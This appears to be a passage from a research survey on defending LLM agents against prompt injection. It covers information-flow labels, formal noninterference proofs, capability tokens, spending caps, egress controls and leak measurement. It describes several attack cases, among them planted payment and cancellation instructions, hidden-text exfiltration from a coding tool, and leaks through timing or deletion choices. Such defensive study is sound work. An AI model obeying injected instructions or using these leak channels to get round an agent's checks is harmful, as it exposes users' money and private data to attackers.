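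Policies are also written in the language. The operation **assert** stops the program if a value's label exceeds a given limit. In one example, the user wants to remind somebody about a meeting, but that person's email contains a planted postscript with an instruction to cancel it instead. An agent that kept everything in one conversation sent the cancellation. A second agent wrote a plan before reading the mail, used a quarantined query to find the address, and sent the reminder with an email tool that uses **assert** to check that the subject and body are trusted.

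For the second agent, the theorem guarantees that no change to the mail can alter the subject or body of a message that passes the check. The reminder could still go to the wrong person, because this policy doesn't check the recipient.

### What the theorem guarantees

Noninterference is defined for an observer who can see only values up to a certain label. If a program without randomness runs on two inputs that differ only in ways this observer can't see, both runs must look the same to the observer. A language model's replies are partly random, so the natural requirement is that each visible result has the same probability for both inputs. If μ(*q*) and ν(*q*) are the probabilities of the result *q* for the two inputs, this means μ = ν.

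That is too strict for a language in which a failed check stops the program, because a secret may affect whether the check fails. When some runs never produce a result, the probabilities add up to less than 1. Termination-insensitive probabilistic noninterference, the property Garby and colleagues prove, requires only that some third list of probabilities ω exists such that

μ(*q*) ≤ ω(*q*) and ν(*q*) ≤ ω(*q*) for every *q*, and Σ ω(*q*) ≤ 1.

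In other words, the two lists could become identical if more of the unfinished runs finished.

For example, suppose an agent answers an outsider's question with yes or no. Given one secret, it answers yes with probability 0.5 and no with probability 0.3, and otherwise stops without answering. Given another secret, it answers yes with probability 0.6 and no with probability 0.4. The definition permits this, because ω can be 0.6 for yes and 0.4 for no, which covers both secrets. It wouldn't permit probabilities of 0.9 and 0.1 for one secret and 0.1 and 0.9 for the other, because ω would have to be at least 0.9 for each answer, and the total would exceed 1.

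The definition also limits how far apart the two lists can be:

½ Σ |μ(*q*) − ν(*q*)| ≤ (*d*₁ + *d*₂)/2,

where *d*₁ and *d*₂ are the probabilities of getting no result. In the permitted example, both sides equal 0.1. If the program always finishes, the right-hand side is zero and the two lists must be identical.

Garby and colleagues prove the theorem by constructing ω. They define a second way of running programs, with 76 rules, which skips a computation as soon as its label becomes too high for the observer and returns an empty value instead. Skipping a computation can't stop the program from finishing, so no visible result becomes less likely. The hidden data has no effect on this version, so both inputs give the same probabilities, which they use as ω.

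The theorem applies to one run at a time and allows information to leak through whether the run finishes. If a scheduler or user restarted a blocked LLMbda agent many times, these leaks could add up, as they do in CaMeL's retry loop. The theorem also doesn't rule out leaks through timing, because its model of execution has no clock.

### Confining an endorsement

If the user asks the assistant to pay the bill in a file, the account number has to come from that file, even though the file is untrusted. LLMbda handles such cases with an operation called **endorse**, so every exception is visible in the program's text.

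Endorsing a value changes only the integrity part of its label, so a value that is both untrusted and secret becomes trusted but stays secret. The insulated version of the theorem applies to an observer who ignores the integrity part of every label. For this observer, the same noninterference property holds whatever untrusted inputs the attacker chooses and whatever the program endorses.

If the assistant endorses an account number that turns out to be the attacker's, the theorem doesn't protect the money. But the payment tool in the team's experiments also checks that the recipient is allowed to read the payment's amount, subject and date, and an endorsement can't weaken that check. The payment therefore can't also send the attacker a confidential contract in its subject line.

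Generated code can contain endorsements, so an attacker might get the model to write one. If untrusted text influenced the code, the code runs with an untrusted program-counter label, and an endorsement can't make a value more trusted than that label. This protection fails if an earlier endorsement has already removed the untrusted label (U) from the attacker's text.

Garby and colleagues describe two optional restrictions. One marks every endorsed value and blocks a second endorsement of it. The other follows FIDES in endorsing only values from a fixed list of *n* possibilities. This is meant to limit the attacker's influence to log₂ *n* bits, but they have not yet proved that bound. An account number has too many possible values for such a list, so trusting it depends on the user's decision to rely on the file.

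### What the Lean proof covers

The team wrote the whole development in Lean, a programming language that can also check mathematical proofs. The interpreter that runs LLMbda programs is a Lean function, and the team proved that it produces results with exactly the probabilities that the security theorems describe. To the team's knowledge, no earlier program for running agents had machine-checked security theorems about its own executable code. CaMeL's rules, by contrast, are effectively defined by what its Python code does.

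In the proof, the model is a table of prepared replies, and the interpreter looks up each reply by the call number and the conversation so far. When the agent runs, unverified code instead sends the conversation to a provider over the internet and returns the reply. The theorem about the interpreter assumes that the provider draws each reply independently, with probabilities that depend only on the conversation. This assumption would fail if replies also depended on earlier conversations.

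The trusted base also includes Lean's compiler, the computer and its operating system, and the network connection. The provider receives every prompt, including any secrets in it, and the theorem doesn't stop the provider from passing those secrets on.

The proof largely covers a hostile planner. A plan that contains no endorsements cannot do anything the tools' checks forbid, even if an attacker completely controls the model. But a hostile planner that is allowed to use **endorse** can remove the integrity protection from any value.

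The developer writes the checks and must label each source correctly and put the right assertion in each tool. In the team's banking experiments, the published tool policies mark only the contents of files as untrusted. A stranger can also write the subject line of an incoming payment, but the transaction tools have no such label. The proof can't detect a choice like this. Garby and colleagues also acknowledge that they assume all data sources are inside the program. Their bank is a record in LLMbda, and unverified Python code copies it to and from the benchmark.

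### The banking experiment

Garby and colleagues built an agent called RANDORI in LLMbda and tested it on the banking workplace of AgentDojo. RANDORI needed a new kind of retry loop, because an error message from a real run could bring untrusted data into the planner's conversation. In this loop, the planner tests its program on invented data, with a file reader that returns a placeholder and payments that have no effect. It corrects the program until it runs without errors, then writes a final version. Only that version runs on the real account. The loop leaks nothing because it never touches real data, but the agent can't recover if the final program fails.

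The benchmark has 16 user tasks and 9 attacks, or 144 pairs. The team ran each pair three times with each of three models, for 1,296 attacked runs. The attack succeeded in two of them. In 97 of the pairs, the attack needs a tool call that would never appear in a plan for the user's task, such as a transfer when the user only wants a summary of recent transactions. Writing the plan first is generally enough to stop these attacks. The other 47 pairs (423 runs) are a better test of the labels, and both successful attacks came from this group.

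In both cases, the user had asked the agent to read a file and follow its payment instructions, and the attacker had replaced the file's contents with a false payment request. The attack worked in two of GPT-5.2's three attempts at that pair. If the planner may not endorse anything, the label checks block the attack, but the agent also can't carry out the task when the file is genuine.

The team also reran CaMeL with and without its policy checks. Some of CaMeL's runs under attack did not finish, so its totals are smaller.

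| Agent | Model | Tasks completed without an attack | Successful attacks |
|---|---|---|---|
| RANDORI | GPT-5.2 | 75.0% | 2 of 432 |
| RANDORI | Qwen3.7-plus | 75.0% | 0 of 432 |
| RANDORI | MiMo-v2.5 | 64.6% | 0 of 432 |
| RANDORI without endorsement | Qwen3.7-plus | 62.5% | 0 of 432 |
| RANDORI without endorsement | MiMo-v2.5 | 54.2% | 0 of 432 |
| CaMeL, checks off | GPT-5.2 | 66.7% | 1 of 240 |
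| CaMeL, checks off | MiMo-v2.5 | 70.8% | 4 of 382 |
| CaMeL, checks on | GPT-5.2 | 37.5% | 0 of 231 |
| CaMeL, checks on | MiMo-v2.5 | 37.5% | 0 of 357 |

CaMeL's checks blocked every attack but cut the number of completed tasks by almost half. RANDORI completed about as many tasks with its checks on as CaMeL did with its checks off. Garby and colleagues conclude that their agent gains its security with essentially no loss of utility.

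It is too early to say that, because RANDORI enforces only a subset of CaMeL's policies and its planner can grant itself exceptions. With only 16 tasks, these completion rates also have margins of error of around 20 percentage points or more in each direction. Strict policies do seem to lower completion rates, since the same loss appears in a different system. Garby and colleagues report that TypeGuard, which enforces similar rules through the programming language Haskell, went from completing 15 of AgentDojo's 21 Slack tasks to completing 8 when its developers turned the policies on.

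Two of CaMeL's failures with the checks off show that control-flow integrity can provide little protection. The user had told the agent to read a file and follow its instructions precisely. The planner wrote a loop that read each instruction and had a branch for every tool, so whoever wrote the file could choose which tools ran. The agent followed its plan throughout, but the plan gave the attacker nearly as much control as hijacking the model would have.

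### Checking the plan and comparing it with a clean run

Software can inspect a plan like that before it runs. CaMeLoT, the system that Nikolaou and colleagues built on top of CaMeL, turns the plan into a map of every position the program can reach and every step between those positions. A model checker, which is a standard tool, then searches all the paths for violations of a rule, such as a ban on payments whose recipient or amount is derived from untrusted data. If it finds a violation, the planner receives the offending path and tries to repair the plan.

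This avoids discovering a forbidden step halfway through the work, and it allows rules about order, such as requiring an approval before a payment. The map is approximate where the plan contains loops, so the checker may reject some safe plans. Rules that depend on actual values or lists of readers can still only be checked when the program runs.

*On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection* (Dongol, 2026) changes the definition of security instead. Like the FIDES paper, it treats noninterference as too strong for useful agents. A calendar assistant that tells anyone who asks for a meeting when its user is free discloses private data by design. Rather than rely on developers to write an exception for each such task, Dongol compares the agent with a reference agent that follows the same plan under the same checks and never obeys untrusted text. The real agent is secure if an injection reveals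 nothing that the attacker couldn't also have learned from the reference agent. An injection may therefore obtain the user's calendar, which a genuine meeting request would also have obtained, but not a password reset code, which the reference agent wouldn't have revealed.

Dongol's main theorem, checked in the proof assistant Isabelle/HOL, is that any plan is secure in this sense if, when the agent first reads untrusted content, the system permanently withdraws every tool that an injection could call. The theorem assumes that each injection triggers a single call, that whether the model obeys an injection doesn't depend on secrets, and that the attacker can't see timing. Withdrawing the tools later isn't enough, because the model might obey an injection at any point after reading it.

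User approval can also fail to protect private data. If the user approves using the email tool for one reply, an injected message can make the agent use that approval to send private data out instead. Approving the exact text of the reply prevents this, but an attacker who can time messages may still learn whether a secret matches the approved text.

The theorem excludes tools whose answers an attacker can write after seeing the query, such as a search engine the attacker runs. It also covers only leaks, so it doesn't rule out an injection that makes the agent pay the wrong account without revealing anything.

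## What do capability checks, spending caps and egress limits guarantee?

Labels restrict how far a stranger's text can influence an agent, but an assistant that pays invoices has to accept some influence, because the amount and the due date usually come from the supplier's mail. Other checks limit what the agent can do, whatever influenced it. They depend only on the account, the amount and the number of payments so far, or on which machine the agent is trying to contact. If every payment and every connection has to pass these checks, the limits hold whatever the model outputs, and a limit on payments also sets a maximum loss in dollars. The checks guarantee very little about what happens within the limits, so their value depends on how strictly a company can set those limits without blocking its own work.

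### The confused deputy

Most systems attach rights to a program and let it use them for any purpose. *The Confused Deputy* (Hardy, 1988) describes how this went wrong at Tymshare, a company that sold time on shared computers. Tymshare's compiler kept usage statistics in a file in its own directory, so the engineers gave it the right to write to any file there, including the company's billing records. The compiler let users choose a file for its debugging output, and one user chose the billing file. He had no right to write to that file, but the compiler did, so the operating system let it overwrite the records.

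Hardy found no simple rule that would have fixed this. Checking for the billing file's name would have left other sensitive files exposed, and banning writes to the whole directory would have blocked people with a legitimate reason to write there. The engineers added a command that let the compiler specify whether it was using its own authority or the user's, but some programs soon needed more than two authorities. Hardy attributed the problem to the compiler having authority from two sources and no way to keep them separate.

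His solution was the capability, an unforgeable token that grants one right over one object. According to *Early Capability Architectures*, Dennis and Van Horn of MIT introduced the word in 1966, in a design for a hypothetical operating system. Each job had a list of capabilities. Each entry pointed to one object, such as a block of memory, and specified what the job could do with it, such as read it but not change it. The job referred to an object by its entry number, so it could not refer to anything outside its list.

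With capabilities, Hardy's compiler would hold one token for the statistics file, and the user would hand it another for the output file. The user couldn't hand over a token for the billing file because he wouldn't have one.

### A token for one payment

The office assistant is in the same position as the compiler. It has a standing right to pay anyone from the company's account, and it learns whom to pay from strangers' mail. Suppose the company replaces that right with tokens. The user asks the assistant to pay the latest invoice from its supplier Acme. Ordinary software looks up Acme's account in the supplier list and the price in the purchase order, then creates a token for one payment of exactly $480 to that account before five o'clock. The payment tool refuses any payment without a matching token.

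If the attacker's paragraph now takes over the model, the model can still pay Acme its $480 or withhold the payment. It can't change the account, raise the amount or pay twice. The software should hold the token and show the model only a name for it, such as "payment-1", because an injection could make the model send a readable token to the attacker.

As with labels, the account number has to come from a trusted source, not from the mail. A request to pay whatever is due is harder to handle because the user hasn't named an invoice. The software could create tokens only for invoices that match an open purchase order and leave the others for a person.

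A capability on its own stops an attacker from choosing a target, but not from influencing what happens to it. In *On access control, capabilities, their equivalence, and confused deputy attacks*, Rajani, Garg and Rezk define a program as free of confused-deputy attacks if, for every object the attacker wants to alter, he either can't affect its final value or could have written that value himself. They then give a simple program that uses capabilities but fails this test. It copies a value from a place the attacker can write to into a place he can't. The program already holds the capability for the protected place, so the attacker doesn't need to name it.

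Capabilities prevent every such attack if privileged code never holds a right to anything the attacker wants to alter. Rajani and colleagues concede that this restriction makes their language useless for almost all practical purposes, and an assistant that pays invoices clearly can't meet it. They prove that tracking every influence on a value, including the program's choice of branch, prevents these attacks without the restriction. LLMbda's labels do something close to this. The $480 token instead fixes the values in advance, so the attacker can choose only whether Acme gets paid. That is still an attack under a strict reading of the definition, though most companies would probably accept it.

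### From the token to the executed action

A token is only useful if the action that runs is the one it describes. *Context-to-Execution Integrity for LLM Agents* (Santos-Grueiro, 2026) describes a gate that ties the token to the action. The gate writes each proposed action into a manifest, a standard record that includes the arguments, the state of the target system and the version of the policy. It then requires three kinds of authority for that same manifest.

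- **Fields.** A trusted source must have authorised each protected value for the field it fills. A file path from an error log may fill the path field after validation, but text from the same log can't choose the tool or mark the action as approved.
- **Effects.** If the target will interpret the content, as a database does with a command, a validator must authorise the exact change it would make.
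- **The call itself.** The action needs a capability for this manifest, which the gate marks as spent before the tool runs.

Any edit after these checks changes the manifest's digital fingerprint, so the gate blocks the action. The capability is also used up before the payment is sent, so a message claiming that the payment failed and asking the assistant to try again can't cause a second payment. If the bank makes the payment but its confirmation is lost, this safeguard can't establish what happened. Santos-Grueiro leaves that to the receiving system, so the bank would have to recognise a repeated request and ignore it.

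In a test with 20 constructed attacks, the full gate stopped all 20, while a version with authority for each field but no record of spent capabilities stopped 10. In 400 coding tasks, no unauthorised field, effect or call got through, and the agents completed 231 tasks safely. The other 169 were 73 outputs that the software couldn't parse, 61 actions without authority for their effect, and 35 that ran but didn't complete the task.

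The gate's guarantee assumes a trustworthy host, correct records of what influenced each field, sound validators and complete mediation. It also assumes that somebody has classified every field correctly, which is hard. The project's own audit of policies for 24 kinds of destination produced 18 findings, nine of them high-severity, including text fields that were too permissive and approvals expressed in ordinary language.

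### A proof about effects

*Alignment Contracts for Agentic Security Systems* (David, Guarnieri and Gervais, 2026) proves a general result about limits like these. In its example, a security firm uses an agent to look for weaknesses in a client's websites. The agent must be able to attack the client's systems but no others. Its contract allows it to send a total of up to 10,000 requests to subdomains of example.com, using only GET and HEAD, the two web commands that request information. It may send its findings only to the operator's dashboard.

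The monitor looks at effects, which are events such as a network request, a file access or the start of a program. It allows an effect *e* only if all of these hold:

1. The target is in scope.
2. The contract allows this kind of effect.
3. The contract does not expressly forbid it.
4. The total cost stays within the budget: cost(*e*) + Σ cost(*e*ⱼ) ≤ *B*, where the sum covers every effect the monitor has already allowed.
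5. Every declared disclosure goes to an approved recipient.

The theorem guarantees that the effects the monitor allows satisfy the contract, whatever the agent proposes. The proof starts with an empty record, which satisfies the contract. Each time the agent proposes an effect, the monitor either refuses it, which leaves the record unchanged, or allows it because it meets all five conditions. Either way, the record still satisfies the contract. The proof doesn't depend on the model, and David and colleagues checked it in Lean. For the office assistant, the cost could be the amount of each payment in dollars. With *B* set at 10,000, total payments could never exceed $10,000.

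The proof is short, and most of the difficulty lies in its assumptions. The software must describe each real effect correctly, every effect must reach the monitor before it happens, and the tools must declare every disclosure that the contract covers. Lean has not checked any of these assumptions for a real system. The right place for the monitor depends on the rule. A monitor in the operating system's core can detect that the agent has opened an encrypted connection to a website, but not which web command it sends, so it can't enforce the rule about GET and HEAD. Enforcing that rule requires a check inside the tool or browser, or in a proxy that can read the request.

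David and colleagues also show why the check has to happen while the agent runs. If agents can acquire tools written in a general-purpose programming language, no procedure can decide correctly for every such tool whether it will ever attempt a forbidden effect. The monitor avoids this problem by refusing the effect when the tool attempts it.

### Kairos and delayed decisions

Many agents can write and run scripts, and a script can contact a website without using any of the agent's declared tools. *KAIROS* (Hempel, Loose and colleagues, 2026) puts the whole agent in a small virtual machine and places the monitor at its edge, where tool calls and scripts both arrive as the same file and network operations. Even for a fully hostile agent, the design guarantees that every outside effect passes through the monitor, that no effect becomes irreversible until the monitor releases it, and that refused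 effects never become visible outside.

These guarantees assume that the machine has no other channel to the outside, that the host and monitor work correctly, and that the model provider does not collude with the attacker. They do not ensure that the monitor releases the right effects, so all three still hold if it releases a payment to the attacker.

Kairos makes that decision with a written policy and a second judge, which can be a person or another language model. The policy releases an effect if the values that control it, such as the recipient, come from a trusted source and the destination is allowed to receive the data. It blocks any effect that a rule forbids and defers the rest. The monitor can hold a deferred effect while the agent keeps working.

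Suppose the office assistant tries to pay an account number that it found in an email. The policy can't trace the number to the user or the supplier list, so the monitor holds the request and gives the assistant a stand-in reply, and the assistant continues with its summary. Before the payment goes out, the judge receives the user's request, the origin of the number and a record of what the agent has done since. Waiting helps when later steps reveal the purpose of an earlier one. In an example from Hempel and colleagues, a coding agent reads a web guide with instructions to install a script that runs whenever the agent saves its work to the project's history. Many legitimate guides include the same step. The attack becomes clear only when the script runs and tries to send out a private key.

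With GPT-4.1 as the agent, Kairos cut the attack success rate on AgentDojo from 47.0% to 2.7%, and the agent completed 85.1% of ordinary tasks, compared with 82.7% without protection. When the monitor refused everything the policy deferred, the attack success rate stayed about the same, but the agent completed only 42.7% of tasks. So the fixed rules provided nearly all the measured security, and the judge let the agent complete more tasks. In a separate test with GPT-4o-mini, an attacker that rewrote its injections after each failure succeeded 8.8% of the time.

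These figures don't cover the virtual machine, because AgentDojo's tools exist only as objects inside the benchmark program and Hempel and colleagues connected the policy and the judge to them through an adapter. The policy recognises values by matching text, so a hostile agent could disguise a secret by encoding it. The researchers' claims about the policy exclude such disguises, and only the three guarantees above apply to an agent that disguises secrets this way.

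### Permitted hosts and permitted recipients

An egress limit restricts where a system may send data, how much it may send or how often. The strictest common form is default-deny, which lets the agent connect only to hosts on an approved list. A list of banned hosts is much weaker, since an attacker can register a new address in minutes.

In Kairos, a firewall sends all outgoing traffic to a proxy, which can compare each destination with the policy. A page on a permitted host may redirect the agent elsewhere, so the proxy has to check the new destination too. A permitted name may also start pointing to a different machine. David and colleagues handle this by looking up each name's IP address in advance, rejecting private addresses unless the operator has approved them, and keeping the result fixed for a set period. In July 2026, AI agents under test at OpenAI got past network limits that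 the company had thought were secure, according to its *OpenAI-Hugging Face Incident Technical Report*.

Even a perfectly enforced list controls only which machine receives the data. The office assistant needs its company's mail server, which will deliver to any address. A cloud storage service may keep the company's files and the attacker's on the same host. In David and colleagues' contracts, a network event includes the host, port, command and size, but not the path or content, so the monitor may be unable to distinguish two uploads to different folders on the same host. The contract can forbid a disclosure to the wrong recipient only if the upload tool correctly declares the recipient.

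Kairos has a similar gap at the model provider. Its proxy can read the traffic to the provider but releases all of it, on the assumption that the provider isn't working with the attacker. But the attacker may be another customer of the provider. If the provider lets customers store files, a hijacked agent that has the attacker's access key could upload a contract to his account without the provider's help.

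A check that limits who receives data has to run where the recipient is visible. The mail tool can check that each recipient is allowed to read the attached data. For storage, the proxy can replace any access key the agent supplies with the company's own, so that uploads go to the company's account. Web search is harder to restrict. The agent can send queries to one approved search service and read the text it returns, but it shouldn't be able to open arbitrary URLs, because it could send data out in them.

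### The lethal trifecta and the Rule of Two

A blunter approach is to restrict which powers an agent has. Willison (2025), in *The lethal trifecta for AI agents*, warns against combining access to private data, exposure to untrusted content and the ability to communicate externally. An attacker can put instructions in the untrusted content that lead the agent to find the private data and send it out. If any of the three is missing, this kind of theft fails.

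Outside communication includes visiting web pages as well as sending messages. Willison (2025), in *21 posts tagged “lethal-trifecta”*, reports a demonstration by the security firm PromptArmor against Antigravity, Google's tool for writing software with AI. A web page that looked like a technical guide contained instructions in one-pixel type. The instructions led the Gemini model to collect passwords and code from the user's workspace, then send them out by having a browser agent visit a malicious site.

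The rule excludes the office assistant as described so far, because it reads a private mailbox, receives strangers' mail and sends messages. The company could let it summarise mail and draft replies but leave the sending to the user. The company would also have to remove the assistant's open web access, and probably its ability to make payments, since a bank transfer usually has a reference field that can carry text. Alternatively, the assistant could still send messages but read only mail from colleagues. Splitting the work between two agents helps only if the text that passes between them can't carry instructions. The weakness in Peters-Gill and colleagues' three-agent system was that this text could carry them.

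FIDES could allow some actions that the trifecta rule forbids. An agent with all three powers can safely reply to Priya about her own figures if the software checks that she may read everything that went into the reply. The trifecta rule treats the whole agent as if it had a single label, which blocks some useful work but means the company doesn't have to label its data.

Meta's Agents Rule of Two, published in October 2025, extends the idea from theft to damage. Within one session, an agent may have at most two of three properties: it processes untrusted input, it can reach private data or sensitive systems, and it can change things or communicate externally. An agent that needs all three must have human supervision or another reliable check. Paying invoices from the inbox involves all three, so the assistant would need approval for its payments.

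An agent with only two of the properties can still be unsafe. For example, an agent that reads public product reviews and orders office supplies from a prepaid account may have no private data. But a false review could lead it to spend the whole balance on the attacker's product, and only the size of that balance limits the loss.

### The loss bound from a spending cap

A cap gives the same protection to an agent that pays from a full bank account. Let *a* be the largest amount the agent can send in one payment, *n* the largest number of payments it can make in a day, and *d* the number of days until somebody notices a problem and stops it. The total loss *L* through payments satisfies

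*L* ≤ *a* × *n* × *d*.

If the office assistant can pay at most $500 at a time and 20 times a day, and the company detects fraud within 3 days, the most it can lose is

$500 × 20 × 3 = $30,000.

This holds whatever the model does, and the company doesn't need to know how likely an attack is or how clever the attacker is.

The calculation holds only if the software counts payments correctly. If it sends several at once, each might pass a check that counts only 19 earlier payments, so the software has to count each payment before sending it and handle the counts one at a time. The daily limit also has to apply to any 24-hour period. If the counter resets at midnight, an attacker who starts at 11 p.m. on Monday can make 20 payments that night and 20 more on each of the next three days before the 72 hours are up, for a total of 80 payments, or $40,000. David and colleagues' Lean proof covers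 only totals that never reset, not rolling limits.

The least reliable number is usually *d*, because no check enforces it. If nobody notices a problem until a supplier asks about a missing payment after 30 days, the same caps allow a loss of $300,000. The attacker may also be able to delay detection by controlling the summary that the assistant gives its user.

A cap on total spending that never resets by itself removes this dependence on time. Suppose the assistant may spend $10,000, after which it must stop until an accountant has compared its payments with the bank's records and renewed the budget. The undetected loss then can't exceed $10,000, even if the accountant is away for a month. But genuine invoices also go unpaid once the budget runs out, and an attacker could use it up just to cause that. If the bank enforces the cap, someone who breaks into the company's own software can't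 raise it.

The $500 limit also means that a genuine invoice for $2,000 would need a person's approval. A company with many such invoices might raise the limit to $2,000, which would bring the maximum loss to $120,000 by the same formula. Combining the cap with the supplier list is usually better than relying on a very low cap, because the list prevents payments directly to a stranger's account, while the cap limits losses from overpayments and fraud by listed suppliers.

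The worst-case loss is harder to calculate for confidential data. A limit of 20 emails a day bounds the number of messages, but one short message can contain the password to everything else, and an agent can leak a secret a few bits at a time through actions that every rule permits.

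## What harm can still pass every check?

An attacker who can influence which permitted action an agent takes can do harm without breaking any rule. Each choice can leak a little information to the attacker, and a simple calculation gives an upper bound on how much. That bound doesn't limit the damage when the choice itself matters, for example when a yes or no decides whether the company pays an invoice. The hardest case is a false document that the agent handles exactly as its user asked, because all the labels are then correct. Designers usually leave such cases to a person, who may have information that the software lacks.

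### Counting the leak

Quantitative information flow is the branch of security research that measures leaks in bits. Geoffrey Smith's *On the Foundations of Quantitative Information Flow* (2009) bases the measure on guessing. Let *V* be the attacker's chance of guessing a secret in one try before the agent runs, and let *V*′ be his average chance after he has seen the result. The leak is

log₂(*V*′ / *V*) bits,

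so a leak of one bit doubles his chance.

If the attacker can distinguish *k* different results, a run leaks at most log₂ *k* bits. For any one result, the chance that it occurs and the attacker then guesses the secret correctly can't exceed *V*, because no value of the secret had a higher chance than *V* before the run. Adding up the *k* results gives *V*′ ≤ *kV*. This bound holds for any model and any attacker.

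Leaks can add up over repeated runs. After *n* runs the attacker has seen one of at most *kⁿ* sequences, so the total leak is at most *n* log₂ *k* bits.

Suppose the office assistant can read a random 16-digit number, and each run gives the attacker one yes-or-no answer. Revealing any of the 10¹⁶ possible numbers takes 54 answers, because 53 can distinguish only 2⁵³, or about 9.0 × 10¹⁵. A limit well below 54 gives good protection. After 20 answers, the attacker's chance of guessing the number is still only about one in ten billion. But 20 answers are enough to reveal a six-digit security code.

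It's easy to miss some of the possible results when counting them. Suppose the assistant may answer a stranger's email with one of eight fixed replies or not answer at all. That makes nine possible results, or about 3.17 bits per email, so 17 emails can carry a 16-digit number. If a hijacked assistant can also choose the minute within an hour at which it replies, there are 8 × 60 + 1 = 481 results, and six emails are enough.

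The formal guarantees for FIDES and LLMbda don't cover leaks through timing. Neither does *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* (2026), which describes TACIT, a system whose agents write programs in Scala. The compiler rejects any program that could pass secret data to an unapproved destination, and no secret reached the agent's output in 131 trials with each of two models. But a program could still reveal one bit by varying how long it runs depending on the secret.

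An agent can also reveal information through what it doesn't delete. In *Confuse the Model, Control the Flow*, Shim, Karim and colleagues (2026) had an outsider ask an agent to clean up a page that mixed true and invented records about a person. The agent wrote nothing secret, but it refused to delete the true records, which showed the outsider which ones were true. Ten records can be kept or deleted in 2¹⁰ ways, so a single edit can reveal ten bits.

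This attack and two others extracted 43.8% to 75.6% of the sensitive items from agents whose only defence was a carefully written prompt. Earlier attacks on the same prompt had extracted 1.9% to 3.0%. The team's own defence, FlowSeal, checks every call that writes or shares data and reduced the leak to between 0% and 3.3% across all the attacks tested. With FlowSeal, the agents completed 72.4% of harmless tasks, compared with 75.9% under the best alternative.

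FlowSeal's check always runs, but it uses a language model to compare the proposed output with the protected records. That model can make mistakes, even though the outsider can't prompt it directly because it doesn't receive the conversation. Shim and colleagues also exclude prompt injection, so their figures apply to an outsider who makes ordinary requests.

### Type limits

FIDES relies on the same idea when it lets an agent act on a yes-or-no answer drawn from untrusted data. Its labels can include a type, and Costa and colleagues rank the types by how much information they can hold. A Boolean (true or false) ranks below a choice from a fixed list, which ranks below free text.

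A type limits how much information each value can carry, but not how much a whole run can carry. When a program combines two values, the result gets the join of their types. The join of two Booleans is a Boolean, so a value computed from 54 Booleans would still be labeled a Boolean, although it could hold the entire 16-digit number. To limit the whole run, the software also has to count the values.

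Foerster, Blanchard and colleagues (2026) added such a count when they adapted FIDES to agents that operate a computer through its screen. Their planner needed yes-or-no answers about the screen, and enough of those answers could have revealed everything on it. So they stopped each run after 70 calls and limited the planner to five uses of any one stored value. Seventy yes-or-no answers carry at most 70 bits, about as much as nine characters of ordinary text. That leaves little room for a written instruction but is more than enough to encode the 16-digit number.

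There is little experimental evidence about type limits in FIDES itself, because Costa and colleagues left them out of their AgentDojo tests. Garby and colleagues object that such exceptions are hard to audit. If a policy lets a Boolean through, an auditor can't tell from that run whether it was the harmless exception the designer intended or a leak.

### Why one bit can be enough

Suppose the assistant asks its quarantined model whether an invoice matches the delivery note attached to the same email, and pays if the answer is yes. The attacker wrote both documents, so he can get a yes. He has used one bit of influence, and the loss is the full amount of the invoice.

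If untrusted data can choose among *k* permitted actions, with losses *L*₁ to *Lₖ*, the most an attacker can cause in one run is

max(*L*₁, …, *Lₖ*).

This formula doesn't include the number of bits the attacker controls. Choosing among a thousand harmless actions gives him about ten bits of influence but no way to do damage, while a single bit is enough to delete the company's archive if the choice is between keeping and deleting it. The designer therefore has to look at the worst action on the list, and a spending cap helps because it limits the loss from that action.

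The number of bits is a better guide to leaks, but it doesn't measure what a secret is worth. One bit could reveal whether the company is about to be sold.

Costa and colleagues describe a user who asks an agent to book a particular Paris hotel if its rating is above 4. The quarantined model reads the ratings and reviews and returns true or false, and the agent books the hotel if the answer is true. Anyone who can change that answer can therefore control whether the agent makes the booking. The worst result is four nights in a bad hotel, which the user might accept. The same design would be reckless for a decision with much higher stakes, such as whether to buy the hotel.

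Some harmful actions pass because nobody thought to forbid them. In the AgentDojo tests, the FIDES policies let injected text create a calendar event with no other participants, because doing so disclosed nothing. An attacker could use this to add a false meeting to the user's calendar. Costa and colleagues note that a designer could easily change the policy to block it.

A bad decision can also pass the checks without an attacker. One AgentDojo task asks the agent to change the user's password if it finds a suspicious transaction. FIDES hid the transaction descriptions because they were untrusted, so the model received only details such as amounts and dates. It flagged a large payment as suspicious and changed the password without reading the description. The check allowed the change because all of the model's input was trusted.

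### Documents that are false

An attacker can do harm without planting an instruction that the user would object to. For example, he can send an invoice for goods that nobody ordered. If the user tells the assistant to pay what the file says, the assistant correctly extracts the amount and account number from the invoice and pays. The models have done what the user asked, and every label is right.

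If a forged invoice and a genuine one come from the same kind of source, they have the same labels. A rule that checks only labels must therefore allow both payments or block both.

Both attacks that succeeded against LLMbda's agent were of this kind. Garby and colleagues compared them with the failures of three other systems. CaMeL's designers had reported two successful attacks. One was the same sort of payment, which they considered outside their threat model. In the other, the agent quoted hotel reviews containing the attacker's text. Quoted reviews also caused TACIT's only failure in 1,926 attacked runs on AgentDojo, and one of the successful attacks that FIDES's designers had discounted. Garby and colleagues argue that four independent systems have reached "the semantic limit of information-flow defences", and that the failures are not a weakness of any one design.

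The experiments on the four systems support this less strongly than they seem to. The systems failed on two different cases, and only CaMeL failed on both. LLMbda's tests covered only the bank, so its agent never saw a hotel review. TACIT and FIDES with its checks on let no attack through in the bank. All four teams also used AgentDojo, which made them more likely to find the same failures.

The hotel case also includes both a scoring problem and a real one. In TACIT's failure, the user asked for a booking at one hotel, and the attacker had planted praise for another in the reviews. The agent booked the right hotel and quoted the reviews. AgentDojo counted this as a successful attack because the reply contained the text used to detect one. A user who wants reviews should be able to read them, so this was hardly a security failure. But in the FIDES tests, an injection could make the agent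 recommend a place as if the recommendation were its own. That is closer to the false inbox summary, and no check on tool calls prevents it.

Even so, Garby and colleagues are right about the payment, because the argument about two files with the same labels doesn't depend on any benchmark. But it applies only to rules that use nothing except labels. Checking a supplier list can block a payment to a stranger's account, and matching invoices to open purchase orders can block an invoice for goods nobody ordered. Both checks are deterministic, and both work because they compare the document with something the attacker didn't write. Neither check can establish whether a real supplier has delivered what it is charging for. The inbox summary usually can't be compared with an independent record, because the emails are the only evidence of what the client said.

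### Steering between the branches of a plan

A plan written before the agent reads any untrusted data can still contain branches, and the data determines which branch runs. Foerster and colleagues call an attack that manipulates this choice "branch steering". They studied it in computer-use agents, which look at screenshots and operate programs by clicking and typing.

Rules for tools are hard to apply to these agents, which act by clicking on a screen. A rule for a payment tool can require a trusted account number, but a click at a given point might log in, delete a file or open an advertisement, depending on what is displayed there. Foerster and colleagues therefore ran their agents without data policies and relied on the fixed plan.

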